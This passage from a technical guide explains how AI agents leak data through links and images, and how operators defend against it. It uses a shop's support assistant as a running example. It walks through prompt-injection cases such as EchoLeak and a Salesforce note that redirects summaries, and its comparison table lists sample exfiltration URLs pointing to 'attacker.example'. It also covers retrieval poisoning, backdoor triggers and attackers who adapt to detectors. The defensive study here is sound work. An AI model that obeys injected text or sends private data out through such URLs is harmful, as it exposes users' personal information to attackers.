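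| Link preview | Usually the messaging company's server | Before the agent posts the message |

The shop can only ask the app not to fetch a page for a preview, because it controls neither the app nor the server that does the fetching. A program that posts to Slack can switch off previews for each message, a remedy that Willison (2024) passes on from the security researcher Johann Rehberger in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*. OpenClaw has a similar setting for Telegram. PromptArmor wants messaging companies to offer such settings for individual chats, but agent developers would still have to use them. Without previews, the customer loses only a thumbnail.

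### Refusing to load images

The simplest defence in a chat window is to show no remote images and make no links clickable. Amazon chose not to render links in Amazon Q for Business, its workplace assistant, after a report of a leak. This defence needs no detector, but the shop's customers would have to copy the refund form's address into a browser by hand. Anyone who does the same with an exfiltration URL will still leak the data.

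A less strict version removes only links and images that point to unapproved sites. A guard that checks the raw text of the answer has to recognise every notation that the chat window will turn into a link. Checking after the chat software has interpreted the text is safer, because each link and image is then a separate object with a known target.

The browser can also enforce the restriction. A Content-Security-Policy is a list of permitted sources that a website sends along with its pages. The shop might send this one:

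`Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' images.shop.example`

The policy permits images from the shop's own site and from `images.shop.example`. The browser checks each image's address against this list before loading it. If the address doesn't match, the browser sends no request, so nothing reaches the attacker's log, however the model wrote the image into the answer. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* says Microsoft used such a policy in May 2023 to stop its Bing chatbot from loading images in general. Rehberger, who writes that blog, had reported the leak.

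The policy has gaps that an operator must fill in other ways. The `img-src` line applies to images, not to links that a user clicks. Desktop and phone apps that draw their own chat window need a separate check. Rehberger found that OpenAI had not added its early protection for ChatGPT to the macOS and iOS apps.

The list of allowed domains also has to be kept current. In 2025, researchers at Noma Security found that the policy for Agentforce, Salesforce's agent product, still permitted a domain whose registration had expired. They registered the domain and used an injected instruction to put sales contacts in the address of an image there. The browser applied the policy correctly and requested the image, which sent the contacts to the researchers' server. Willison reports that Salesforce corrected the list and added a check on the links that the agent writes.

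### EchoLeak

A better-known case involved three safeguards, all of which failed. EchoLeak, also listed as CVE-2025-32711, was a vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot. Researchers at Aim Labs, now part of Cato Networks, showed that an outsider could send an employee an email and later receive private data from Copilot without the employee clicking anything. Copilot only had to retrieve the email while answering one of the employee's questions. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, gives the discoverers' account. In outline, the safeguards failed as follows:

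| Safeguard | What Microsoft meant it to stop | Why it failed |
|---|---|---|
| Injection classifier | Emails containing instructions for the model | The email read like ordinary instructions to an employee |
| Link redaction | Links and images that pointed outside the organisation | The filter did not recognise every notation for them |
| Content-Security-Policy | Images from unapproved domains | The list included a Microsoft service that could itself contact an outside server |

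The list of image sources that Ravia prints has 29 different entries, 11 of which permit every subdomain of a domain. An operator who permits a domain also permits every service on it, including any that will fetch a URL on anyone's behalf.

Microsoft distinguishes probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to succeed, from deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack will fail, and it prefers deterministic defences where possible. EchoLeak only partly supports that preference, because only one of the three safeguards, the classifier, was probabilistic. The other two were fixed rules that worked as written but had gaps. Fixes to such rules are easier to verify, however. An engineer can add a missing notation to a filter and show that it now works, or remove a service from a list. Retraining the classifier offers no such assurance, and Ravia notes that good examples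 of real injections are scarce.

Aim Labs reported the flaw privately in January 2025. According to Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, Microsoft deployed a fix on its own servers in May and published an advisory on 11 June. Customers had nothing to install, and neither company knew of an attack on a customer. Reddy and Gujral add that Microsoft later changed Copilot, which now strips embedded images and the overlooked kind of link from external content. Microsoft also reportedly added options to stop Copilot from accessing external messages in some contexts, though Reddy and Gujral's account of this is second-hand.

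Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click vulnerability in a major AI application, but Rehberger also uses "zero-click" for the leak he reported to OpenAI in 2023. Ravia's narrower claim is more defensible, that earlier attacks either needed the user to point the chatbot at malicious content or tightly limited what could leak.

A year later, in June 2026, the security firm Varonis disclosed a similar problem in Copilot, called SearchLeak. The attack began when the user clicked a crafted link to Copilot's search page. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* notes that ordinary URL filters were unlikely to flag the link because it led to a real microsoft.com address. Data then left through images fetched by Bing, Microsoft's search engine. WinBuzzer's *Microsoft Patches Copilot SearchLeak Data-Theft Flaw* (2026) lists emails, files and two-factor login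 codes among the data attackers could reach. Microsoft patched the flaw, and at disclosure there was no public evidence that anyone had exploited it. Bing was already on the list of permitted image sources that Ravia printed in 2025, so SearchLeak probably relied on a trusted service in much the same way.

### From permitted domains to permitted addresses

A guard can apply the same idea to an agent that opens web pages by checking each domain against an allowlist before the agent fetches the page. OpenAI has two objections to relying on this check.

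A redirect on a permitted site can carry private text elsewhere if the guard checks only the first domain. Even if the guard checks every redirect, a permitted site may itself let strangers read what it receives. Google's Antigravity, a programming tool with a browsing agent, shipped with a default allowlist that included webhook.site, where anyone can create an address and read the requests sent to it. PromptArmor used webhook.site to demonstrate the theft of passwords and code.

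OpenAI also objects that a short list blocks many harmless pages, and that users who see a warning every few minutes learn to click through it. Some evidence for this comes from Anthropic, which had 1,053 paid testers use its programming agent and replaced one permission request in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Willison reports that only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The study tested commands rather than links, and Anthropic published it to promote an automatic alternative, but such a low figure still casts doubt on any defence that depends on frequent confirmation.

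In January 2026 OpenAI described a different rule for ChatGPT, which it calls Safe Url. The agent may fetch an address automatically only if that exact address was already public. The check works like this:

1. A crawler explores the public web, as a search engine does, and records the addresses it finds. It has no access to conversations, accounts or other personal data.
2. When the agent is about to load a page or image, software looks for the complete address in the crawler's records.
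3. If the address is there, the agent loads it.
4. If not, the software tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning.

An address that the crawler found independently of a conversation is unlikely to contain private data from it. The warning displays the address, with a notice that the link is unverified and may include information from the chat. OpenAI uses the same mechanism in its Atlas browser and in Deep Research, its tool for long research tasks. In most of the attacks OpenAI knows of, the model refuses to send the data, so the check is meant for the cases where it doesn't refuse.

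Suppose the support assistant can open web pages, and the shop's allowlist contains only `courier.example`. The customer lives at 14 Mill Lane. The two rules treat five addresses as follows:

| Address the agent wants to open | Domain rule | Exact-URL rule |
|---|---|---|
| `courier.example/help/late`, a public help page | Opens it | Opens it |
| `routerfix.example/reset`, a public page on a small site | Warns needlessly | Opens it |
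| `attacker.example/log?a=14-Mill-Lane` | Warns | Warns |
| `courier.example/go?to=attacker.example/14-Mill-Lane`, a redirect | Opens it and leaks the address | Warns |
| `courier.example/track/8841907`, the customer's own tracking page | Opens it | Warns needlessly |

The second and fourth rows correspond to OpenAI's two objections, and the exact-URL rule handles both correctly. The last row shows a drawback of the rule. The crawler will not have recorded a page made for one customer, because that page is not on the public web, or a page published since the last crawl. A shop that needs tracking pages would do better to give the assistant a dedicated tool for reading them than to train customers to dismiss warnings.

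The comparison must also be strict. Safe Browsing tries shortened versions of an address and counts a match on any of them. This is sensible for detecting dangerous links, but a guard that allows links when they match should not do the same. If it ignored everything after the question mark, a link could carry private text there unnoticed.

OpenAI says the rule protects against quiet leaks through the address itself, but does not establish that a page is trustworthy, that the site won't try to manipulate the user, or that the page contains no harmful instructions for the model. A phishing page that the crawler has recorded passes the check, so a guard still needs the reputation lookup.

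### What still leaks

OpenAI also published a technical paper on the rule, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. Rehberger calls the rule a significant improvement but not a complete solution. ChatGPT had had some form of URL check since December 2023, and he had found ways around the earlier versions. The new rule makes attacks more complicated and limits what they can leak, but it doesn't prevent leaks entirely, because the agent still contacts outside servers and its choice of public pages can reveal a little information. According to Rehberger, OpenAI acknowledges this in the paper. Leaking data this way is much slower than writing a home address into a URL, but a few characters could matter if they belong to a login code.

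Embrace The Red proposes two further measures. The service could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and reuse it, so that a second visit sends no new request. It could also forbid the agent from visiting the same full address twice in a session. Either measure would reduce what an attacker could learn from repeated visits, though some data would still leak. Rehberger had not tested whether OpenAI already does this. He also worries that OpenAI developers building new features may not know the check exists. This worry is reasonable, since the phone and desktop apps are unprotected.

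A rule of this type also depends on who can supply permitted addresses. Anthropic similarly restricts the tool that its model Claude uses to fetch pages. Claude may not open addresses it has composed itself. In September 2025, Willison wrote that the tool accepted addresses from the user, search results or pages it had already fetched. Accepting addresses from fetched pages was a weakness, because an attacker's page could offer Claude a selection of links. A researcher, Ayush Paul, used this weakness to extract a user's name, home city and employer. By July 2026, Anthropic had stopped the tool from following links found in fetched pages. OpenAI's rule is stricter on this point, since its crawler must have seen the address independently. But according to Rehberger, ChatGPT also accepts any address the user types, for the rest of that chat.

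OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) describes a stronger, optional restriction for people who handle especially sensitive data. With the setting on, ChatGPT browses only stored copies of pages. No live request leaves OpenAI's network, so an attacker's server cannot learn which page the agent chose. However, search results may be out of date, ChatGPT may not show images, and Deep Research and agent mode are unavailable. OpenAI thinks most users don't need the setting. Willison welcomed it, but took its existence to imply that ChatGPT's default settings do not robustly protect against a determined attacker.

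OpenAI's help page for the setting, *Lockdown Mode*, warns that data may still escape through connected apps, because an agent that can write to an outside service can leak data through a tool call without opening a link.

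## Detecting injected instructions and poisoned content in text

To stop harmful tool calls as well as harmful links, a guard can look for injected instructions in the text before the model reads it, or it can check each step the model proposes before any software carries it out. Three kinds of detector are in use:

| Detector | Input | Output | Training data | Typical failure |
|---|---|---|---|---|
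| Small classifier | One tool response or retrieved passage | A score, usually from 0 to 1 | Passages labelled as injected or harmless | Flags harmless text that resembles an attack, or misses attacks unlike those in training |
| Language-model judge | The user's request, the steps so far and the proposed step | A verdict, often with a reason | Labelled agent sessions, or nothing beyond a written prompt | Blocks legitimate steps, or changes its verdict with the wording of the prompt |
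| Hidden-state probe | Numbers from inside the model that is reading the text | A score | The same numbers, recorded for labelled text | Works only with the model whose numbers it learned from |

Matching text against written patterns, such as phrases that tell a model to ignore its instructions, is simpler than any of these methods, but it misses most subtle attacks. *Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) tested a pattern-based tool on three public collections of attacks, the largest with 5,968 cases. The tool's detection rate for subtle indirect injections levelled off at about 35% to 45%.

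### Classifiers that score one passage at a time

Dingeto and Leeney (2026), in *AgentRedBench*, built a classifier to check outside text as it enters an AI agent. They work for StackOne Technologies, and their benchmark covers 24 business services, including Gmail, Slack and Salesforce. In one scenario, a user asks an agent to update a customer's record and email a summary to the account's owner. A note in the record says that such summaries now go to a compliance address, which belongs to the attacker. The note looks like routine office administration and contains no instruction to ignore anything.

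AgentRedGuard is a guard model with 142 million parameters (numbers adjusted during training). It reads up to 512 tokens (words or pieces of words) of a tool response and returns the probability that the response contains an attack. If the probability is above 0.5, the guard withholds the response from the agent. It was trained on 660 attacks, all written by two of Anthropic's models, and 3,070 harmless responses.

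Dingeto and Leeney kept four services out of the training data and tested the guard on 133 attacks from those services. It detected 132 of them (99.2%). It raised no false alarms on 110 harmless responses from realistic agent runs, and one on 404 synthetic responses.

With no false alarms in 110 harmless responses, the 95% interval for the false-positive rate runs from 0 to 2.7%. If the true rate is *F*, the chance of seeing no alarm in *n* harmless responses is (1 − *F*)<sup>*n*</sup>, which is still about 5% for a rate of 2.7% and 110 responses. If each of the shop's 1,000,000 daily answers relied on one tool response, a rate of 2.7% would mean 27,000 false alarms a day. The upper limit of the interval is roughly 3/*n*, so the shop would need about 30,000 harmless responses in a row without an alarm to show that the rate is below 0.01%.

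Detection also depends on how closely new attacks resemble the training data. When Dingeto and Leeney left one of three attack types out of training, the guard caught 82% to 89% of the omitted type. It caught 85.5% of attacks written by GPT-5.4-mini and 90.0% of those written by Gemini 3 Flash, though neither model had written any of the training attacks. Dingeto and Leeney chose a small model because these attacks share surface features that it can learn without much understanding of the text. The guard is therefore likely to do worse on attacks without those features.

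They also repeated attacks that had already succeeded against three unprotected models. The guard cut the success rate from between 86% and 88% to about 11%, which is much worse than one miss in 133. The live test was harder because each attack had three attempts and had already worked at least once. It was also easier in one way, because the guard's training data came from runs of the same benchmark.

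### Why results change so much between tests

Dingeto and Leeney tested other guards on the same 133 attacks. Meta's injection classifier, Prompt Guard 2, detected none of them. Protect AI's classifier detected 9.8% of the attacks and flagged 13.6% of the realistic harmless responses. None of these guards had been trained on tool responses, so the comparison favours AgentRedGuard.

A comparison by researchers outside Meta and Protect AI gives a different picture. Liu, Jia and colleagues (2026), in *LongPIBench*, generated 100 long documents of each of four kinds. They inserted text that claimed to come from someone in authority, such as a conference committee or a system administrator. Each cell below gives the share of injected documents detected, followed by the share of harmless documents wrongly flagged:

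| Detector | Research papers | Résumés | Email threads | Code reviews |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt Guard | 38% / 4% | 58% / 0% | 2% / 1% | 63% / 0% |
| Prompt Guard 2 | 100% / 75% | 100% / 41% | 100% / 95% | 95% / 73% |
| Protect AI's classifier | 0% / 0% | 0% / 0% | 0% / 0% | 0% / 0% |
| DataSentinel | 100% / 100% | 100% / 99% | 86% / 77% | 100% / 54% |
| PIShield | 66% / 0% | 55% / 0% | 15% / 0% | 87% / 0% |

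With 100 documents of each kind, each figure could be off by up to about 10 points, but the differences are far larger. Prompt Guard 2 missed every attack in *AgentRedBench* but flagged nearly everything here, including 95 of 100 harmless email threads. Meta offers the model in more than one size, which may explain part of the difference. PIShield has the most usable results, with no false alarms in 400 harmless documents, but it missed 85% of the injected emails. DataSentinel, an earlier detector by some of the same researchers, had done well on short texts.

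Long documents are difficult for any classifier with a short input limit. An operator can split a document into pieces and flag it if the classifier flags any piece, but each additional piece adds another chance of a false positive. A 10,000-token document makes about 20 pieces of 512 tokens, so a false-positive rate of 1% per piece becomes about 18% per document if the errors are independent.

*When Benchmarks Lie* (2026) found the same two extremes in different products. Protect AI's classifier detected 8% of indirect injections and wrongly flagged 4.2% of harmless text. A classifier from deepset detected 99.8% of attacks but flagged 82.4% of harmless text.

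Poor training labels may be part of the problem. Avinash, Pareek and Hada (2025), in *Protect*, collected public and private examples for a commercial guard that covers toxicity, sexism, privacy and injection. They found that many of the original labels reflected keywords rather than meaning. A classifier trained on such labels will learn to react to keywords. The researchers used a larger model, Gemini 2.5 Pro, to relabel 48,218 texts, which changed 10,079 of the labels (20.9%). Of those changes, 9,738 were from violation to harmless. The researchers checked only samples of the new labels. The figures cover all four categories, so they don't give the error rate for injection labels alone.

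The shop's classifier might flag a customer's reasonable question about security. Shire and Kim tested three classifiers on 872 harmless prompts from public collections that discuss security or resemble instructions. One classifier with an excellent score on ordinary test data flagged about a third of them. Even at the most favourable threshold, the best classifier flagged 22.6%. Adding harmless prompts that resemble attacks to the training data nearly eliminated false alarms on prompts the researchers had written in a similar style, but many remained on the public prompts. Shire and Kim chose the public prompts to provoke errors, so these rates are much higher than a typical service would see.

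They also trained each classifier five times, changing only the random starting point. For one design, the best threshold ranged from 0.01 to 0.904. A threshold that works for a classifier may therefore be useless after retraining.

The most demanding test is detection at a fixed, low false-positive rate. *Prompt Injection Detection is Regime-Dependent* (2026) tested LLM Guard's injection scanner on a mix of attacks and harmless prompts containing attack-like language. At a 1% false-positive rate, the scanner detected no attacks, and at 5% it detected 0.29% of them. One of the researchers' own detectors, tested on data similar to its training data, caught 84% of attacks at a 10% false-positive rate but only 10.5% at 1%. Since a deployed guard usually needs a false-positive rate well below 1%, operators should measure detection at that rate on their own tool responses.

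### Judges that compare a step with the user's request

A classifier examines a passage without the user's request, whereas a judge can compare the agent's next step with that request. If the customer asked only where her router is and the agent proposes to email her address to a stranger, the step is suspicious even if the courier's note looks harmless.

Zheng, Li and colleagues (2026), in *StepGuard*, trained a judge model with 4 billion parameters to check each of an agent's tool calls before it runs. The judge receives the user's request, descriptions of the available tools, the agent's earlier steps with their results, and the proposed call. It returns a verdict of safe or unsafe and names the type of risk. A session can contain an injection and still be safe if the agent recognises the injection and doesn't act on it.

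Real records of agents doing dangerous things are rare, so the researchers generated sessions in groups of four. In one session, the agent takes a dangerous step. Two others begin the same way, but the agent then refuses or finds a safe way to finish the task. The fourth uses the same tools for an unrelated, harmless task. A judge trained on these groups can't succeed just by learning that certain tools are dangerous.

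After 3,000 training examples, the judge was too cautious, with 91.1% accuracy on unsafe cases and 69.3% on safe ones. The researchers then used reinforcement learning, which rewards correct verdicts, and gave extra weight to whichever class the judge was getting wrong more often. Accuracy fell to 86.4% on unsafe cases and rose to 78.4% on safe ones. In live tests, the agent completed 5 to 7 percentage points more of its tasks with the extra weighting than with ordinary reinforcement learning, while the attack success rate rose by only 0.3 points.

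Zheng and colleagues ran the finished judge in two environments that test agents against injections. On AgentDojo, 1.2% of attacks succeeded and the agent completed 90.7% of its legitimate tasks. On the harder AgentDyn, 9.3% of attacks succeeded and the agent completed 66.7% of its legitimate tasks. On average across the two, the judge reduced attack success by 77.3% and task completion by 2.8 points compared with no guard.

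The trade-off was worse on AgentHarm, which also includes malicious requests. The guard reduced the score for malicious behaviour from 22.8 to 3.4, but it also reduced completion of harmless tasks by about a quarter, from 70.9% to 52.8%. Other judges erred much further towards caution. In one of the researchers' comparisons, AgentDoG accepted only 26.5% of safe cases and ShieldAgent 42.3%.

A judge has less evidence of an attack when the injected action fits within the user's request. In the Salesforce scenario, the user asked the agent to email a summary, so the proposed step looks right except for the recipient. Checking the recipient requires information about who owns the account, which a lookup in the customer database can determine more reliably than a language model can.

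An operator can also skip the training and prompt a general model to act as the judge, but its accuracy then depends heavily on the wording of the prompt. *When Benchmarks Lie* tested four prompts for one judge on 10,054 texts. Detection of indirect injections ranged from 11% to 93%, and the false-positive rate from 1.4% to 18.9%. A published result for such a judge is therefore of little use without the prompt.

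Larger models are not always better detectors. *BrowseSafe++* (2026) compared prompted models with a trained detector of 0.8 billion parameters on web pages. The small detector scored 98.29 out of 100 on F1 when reading the pages' HTML, while Claude Opus 5.5 scored between 84.44 and 86.50, depending on the format. Opus had the lowest false-positive rate of the frontier models, between 3.77% and 4.84%. The small detector shares the benchmark's name and probably trained on similar pages, so its lead may shrink elsewhere. Converting the pages to markdown lowered detection by about 14 to 16 points, even though the full injection was still in the text.

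The same study gives a reason to run detection as a separate step. Fifteen models judged whether pages contained attacks and, in a different test, carried out tasks on those pages. When a model followed an injection, it had flagged the page in the judging test 74.15% of the time. Models can apparently recognise an attack and still obey it while working on something else. A guard that runs detection separately and uses ordinary code to block the step could stop many of these attacks without a better model.

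### Probes that read the model's hidden states

As a language model processes text, each of its layers produces long lists of numbers called hidden states. A probe is a small classifier that takes the protected model's hidden states as input, so it doesn't have to process the text itself.

In *Safety Beyond the Interface*, Khatri, Prabhu and Neogi (2026) built probes to detect harmful prompts to Llama 3.1 8B. They ran labelled prompts through the model and saved the 4,096 numbers that its final layer produced at the last token. They then trained a 12.6-million-parameter network to classify prompts as harmful or harmless from those numbers. Its F1 scores were 99.1% on WildJailbreak, 82.7% on BeaverTails and 83.5% on AEGIS 2.0, where the 8-billion-parameter Llama Guard 3 had scored 77.3%.

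These tests measure detection of harmful content, such as violence and hate speech, not of instructions hidden in tool results. A courier's note that redirects an email contains nothing violent or hateful. Khatri and colleagues also used only the plain requests in WildJailbreak, not the disguised ones, which probably helps explain the 99.1%. They argue that attackers who can't see the model's hidden states can't easily counter a probe. That may be true of outsiders, but they did not test it, and they list robustness to attack as future work.

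*When Benchmarks Lie* tested a probe on indirect injections. At a false-positive rate of 3.5%, the probe detected 68.2% of them, compared with 46.0% for the best practical version of the prompted judge. This is better evidence that hidden states contain useful information about injections, though the probe still missed nearly a third of them.

Probes are also hard to deploy. The shop can use one only if it runs the model itself or the provider offers access to the hidden states. When the provider updates the model, the hidden states change and the probe will probably need retraining, while a text classifier or judge can stay in place.

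### Planted passages in a document store

None of these detectors is well suited to catching a passage that is simply false, such as the forged returns policy described earlier. If the passage is fluent, a text detector has little to flag, because whether the passage is true depends on facts outside the text.

In some older attacks, a program searched for strings of words that pushed a document to the top of the results. These strings often looked like gibberish, which made the attacks easier to find. A filter can catch them by measuring perplexity, which is how poorly a language model predicts the text. *RAGPart & RAGMask* (2025) found that such filters catch machine-optimised text but cannot distinguish readable poisoned documents from honest ones.

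Removing duplicates doesn't help much either. *TriShieldRAG* (2026) examined generated passages that all supported the same false answer but were worded differently, so a check for identical copies removed none of them. The passages were also closely related to the target question, and search systems rank such passages highly. A guard that rejected passages for being too relevant would also reject the best legitimate ones.

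Run-time checks therefore need evidence from outside the single passage, starting with whether sources agree. *ToxicRAG* (2026), a study of poisoning attacks, describes a defence called RobustRAG. In outline, the model answers the question from each retrieved passage alone, and the system combines the answers. If one of five passages is false, the other four can outvote it.

Voting works only if most of the retrieved passages are genuine and address the question. In one test, *SilentRetrieval* (2026) planted three documents for each question. The attack got its text into the top ten results 94.3% of the time and misled the model 69.2% of the time. Voting can also fail when there are too few passages. The shop may have only one page about returns, so there is nothing to compare a forged page with. When the shop does change its policy, the new page will disagree with years of old tickets, and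 a vote would favour the outdated answer.

A monitor can also measure how much each retrieved passage affects the answer. *RAGuard* (2026) has the model answer once with all the passages and then again with each one removed. A passage should be checked further if removing it changes the answer. With five passages, this takes six answers instead of one. The method could miss two planted passages with the same message, because removing one leaves the other in place and the answer may not change. It would also flag a legitimate page if that page were the only relevant one in the store.

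*Tracing Target Answers in Poisoned Retrieval Corpora via Token Influence Attribution* (Chen, Chen and colleagues, 2026) presents TRACE, a method that looks for words that have a strong influence in several passages, then checks whether those words change the model's prediction. TRACE can also reveal the answer the attacker wanted, which would help an analyst find other planted documents. Legitimate passages often repeat the correct answer too, so false alarms are a risk.

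A guard can flag retrieved passages whose numerical encodings lie far from the rest. *Rescuing the Unpoisoned* (2025) uses light machine learning to filter suspect passages after retrieval. *SilentRetrieval* applies several defenses in sequence. It first checks for perplexity and unusual encodings, then uses a second model to reorder the passages, and then limits the influence of any single passage. The light filters alone were not enough, and combining checks at retrieval with checks during answering worked best.

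Provenance, the record of where a document came from, is probably the most useful evidence for the shop. The document store can record who added each passage and when, and the shop can limit the assistant to policy pages published by its own staff. A forged policy in a customer's ticket then fails the check, however convincing it is, because the rule is fixed and requires no judgement about the text. The rule doesn't work if an attacker takes over a staff account or if staff copy a false claim into a trusted page. It also doesn't help an assistant that answers from the open web, where anyone can publish.

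### Models that misbehave on a trigger

Poisoned training data can leave a backdoor in the model, a behaviour that appears only when the input contains a certain trigger. The trigger can be an ordinary word or topic, so a guard has to look at what the model does.

*TraceGuard* (Guo, Shi and colleagues, 2026) checks the intermediate reasoning steps that many current models write out before they answer. Its verifier, a separate small model, labels each step as supported or unsupported by the question and the steps before it, then gives a verdict on the reasoning as a whole. In one of the paper's examples, a problem requires 813 − 125, but the reasoning changes this to 813 + 125, and every later calculation follows correctly from the wrong sum. A check of only the later arithmetic would miss the error.

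The researchers first trained the verifier on 4,000 checked examples. They then used reinforcement learning to reward it for finding the right step as well as reaching the right verdict. They tested it on 4,100 new examples from three families of attack. In the first, the reasoning contains a rule that the task does not support. In the second, a hidden condition switches the model to a different way of reasoning. In the third, the model produces an answer first and then makes up a justification for it.

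A verdict counted only if the verifier had labelled every step correctly. A 4-billion-parameter verifier scored 94.4, 91.0 and 95.0 out of 100 on the three families, while an untrained 20-billion-parameter model scored 42.2, 32.2 and 40.1. Some of this gap comes from the strict scoring, because the larger model scored between 73.8 and 78.4 on individual steps but seldom got a whole example right.

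The verifier also made mistakes on harmless reasoning. It got everything right on 99.5% of commonsense problems, 95.1% of symbolic ones and 90.6% of arithmetic ones. Some of the errors were wrong step labels rather than false alarms, but an error rate near 10% would be too high for a customer service system. With suitable instructions, the commercial model GPT-5.6 Terra did better, scoring at least 99.6 on every attack family. Guo and colleagues prefer a small local verifier because it keeps the reasoning inside the organisation and avoids a charge for every query.

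The problems were mostly school mathematics, commonsense questions and symbolic puzzles, so the method's performance on real business tasks is unknown. It also requires the model's full reasoning, which a provider may not supply, and it can find a backdoor only if that reasoning shows an unsupported step. For instance, the agents in the BACK-REVEAL experiment could have leaked their session memory without any visible error in reasoning.

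### When attackers know the detector

Detection falls sharply when attackers know which detector they face and adapt to it. In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), such attackers got past every detector tested, even when the system combined several. Most of the figures above come from fixed sets of attacks, so they don't measure detection against attackers who adapt. Zheng and colleagues, for example, say their tests of StepGuard did not cover adaptive attackers.

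The best argument for fixed rules comes from *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026), which tested nine defences with an automated attacker that learned from each failure over hundreds of rounds. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually failed. When ordinary application code checked the model's answers, no secrets leaked in 15,000 attacks. The task suited this check because the secrets were known in advance. This method would also let the shop search its answers for a known password, but not detect a false returns policy.

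Defenders of detectors argue that they can be worth having even if a determined attacker can beat them. *The Attacker Moves Second* itself calls detectors a "useful—but limited" component, since they are easy to deploy and block some unsophisticated attacks. *LLMail-Inject* (2025) provides some evidence from a public challenge in which people tried to make an email assistant send unauthorised messages and could revise their attempts. The defences included Microsoft's Prompt Shield, a probe called TaskTracker and a language-model judge. Many emails tricked the assistant into making the tool call the attacker wanted but failed because a detector caught them.

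Adaptive attacks also don't always defeat a defence completely. *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (2026) tested several defences on one small model and took the most successful attack against each. On average, these attacks succeeded 21.7% of the time when they were fixed and 41.8% when they could adapt. Not all of the defences were detectors, so these figures are only a rough guide to how much adaptation reduces detection.

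If an attacker has to try many versions against the shop's live system, each failed attempt may alert an analyst, who can then remove the planted document or block the account that added it. The shop loses some of this advantage when the detector is public. AgentRedGuard's weights, for instance, are free to download, so an attacker can practise on a private copy and send the shop only the version that works.

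## Checking an answer while it is being streamed

Most of the detectors described so far read a finished text, such as a tool response or a proposed step, but the front end displays the answer to the customer while the model is still writing it. Streaming lets the customer start reading almost at once. If the model writes 50 tokens a second, she would otherwise wait 12 seconds for a 600-token answer.

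A guard is most accurate when it has the whole answer, because a later sentence can change the purpose of an earlier one. *From Judgment to Interference* (Li, Sheng and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of an answer that begins responsibly, warning that poaching is illegal and damages local communities, but then offers a step-by-step guide for anyone determined to do it.

### Hold, check in chunks, or retract

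The safest design holds the full answer until it has been checked. The gateway collects all 600 tokens, the guard checks them, and the front end displays the answer only if it passes. The customer sees nothing for 12 seconds plus the time for one check, then sees the whole answer at once. The detector can still make mistakes, but none that come from checking only part of the answer. This is also the only design that allows a warning about links at the top of the answer, as in Han and colleagues' Wildflare.

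A compromise is to release the answer in checked chunks. The gateway collects 200 tokens, and the guard checks them before the front end displays them. The guard then checks the next 200 tokens together with the last 50 of the previous chunk, called the overlap. The first words appear after 4 seconds plus the time for one check, and the rest arrives in bursts. The guard can miss harmful content if it needs more context than the chunk and the overlap contain.

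The fastest design releases each token immediately while the guard checks a copy of the stream in the background, so the check adds no delay. If the guard finds a problem, it stops the stream, and the front end has to remove the text already on the screen. The customer can read the bad text, click a link or copy a command before the front end removes it.

Smaller chunks shorten the wait but require more checks. Kong's *AI AWS Guardrails Policy* describes the same trade-off for its gateway. With chunks of 50 tokens and an overlap of 20, the shop's customer would see the first words after about a second, but the guard would run 12 times instead of 3, with less context each time.

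Streaming is useful only when a person is reading the output. The support agent's tool calls and its messages to the billing agent should wait for a full check, because the shop can't easily reverse a refund.

### A link split across two chunks

Suppose the answer contains the phishing link `https://shop.example.refund-help.example/form`. The link starts with the shop's name but leads to a site run by the owner of `refund-help.example`. It runs from token 195 to token 210, and the first chunk ends at token 200, just after `https://shop.example`.

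The first check finds the address of the shop's own site and passes it. Without overlap, the second check starts at `.refund-help.example/form`. A pattern for "https" matches nothing there, so the guard passes the second chunk too. The browser then joins the two parts into a working phishing link. With an overlap of at least six tokens, the second check would have included the whole address.

The boundary can fall anywhere in an address. In the worst case, only the last of the address's *L* tokens lands in the second chunk, so the overlap must include at least the other *L* − 1 tokens, which is 15 in this example.

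The default overlap in NeMo Guardrails is 50 tokens, according to NVIDIA's *Output Rail Streaming Configuration*, so any address of up to 51 tokens fits entirely within at least one check. An exfiltration URL with encoded data in its subdomain can be longer than that. If the URL has 80 tokens and starts at token 130, the first check ends at token 200 and includes only part of the host name. The second check starts at token 151 and leaves out the first 21 tokens of the address. A larger overlap allows for longer addresses, but an attacker can make the address longer still.

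Overlap also doesn't remove text that the guard has already released, so users can see the first part of blocked content that crosses a chunk boundary. This is an exception to the guarantee in NVIDIA's documentation that users never see blocked content if the guard checks each chunk first. In the example, the customer would be left with a harmless link to the shop, but if the answer contained a 16-digit card number, half the digits could already be on the screen.

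For links, a guard can avoid both problems by never releasing part of an address. When the text so far ends in what could be the start of an address, the guard holds that part back until a space or closing bracket marks the end. It then checks the complete address and releases it if it passes, so only links are delayed. The guard also needs to block any address over a maximum length, so that a very long one can't stall the answer.

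### What products do with streamed answers

Products differ in which design they use by default. The table compares NeMo Guardrails with three other products, based on AWS's *Configure streaming response behavior to filter content*, Microsoft's *Content streaming* and OpenAI's *Streaming vs Blocking*:

| Product | Default | Alternative |
|---|---|---|
| NeMo Guardrails, with streaming enabled | Sends each chunk, then checks it | Checks each chunk, then sends it |
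| Amazon Bedrock Guardrails | Checks each chunk, then sends it | Sends text at once and blocks later chunks if it finds a problem |
| Azure OpenAI content filters | Check each chunk, then send it | Send text at once and report a problem within about 1,000 characters |
| OpenAI's Guardrails library | Checks the whole answer without streaming | Streams at once and checks in parallel |

In NeMo, a setting called `stream_first` is on by default and sends text to the customer before the guard checks it. If the guard then blocks a chunk, the stream ends with an error message, but the customer already has the text. An operator who sets a chunk size of 200 may wrongly assume that the guard checks 200 tokens before the customer sees them.

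The faster modes of Bedrock and Azure have other drawbacks. Bedrock cannot mask sensitive information in its asynchronous mode, so the shop could not use that mode to replace a home address with a placeholder. On Azure, the customer's own application has to retract the flagged text. In one of Microsoft's sample streams, a user asks for song lyrics, and the filter stops the answer after nearly 1,000 characters have been sent. Microsoft recommends the default mode for customer-facing chatbots in regulated industries and the faster mode for uses such as internal development tools.

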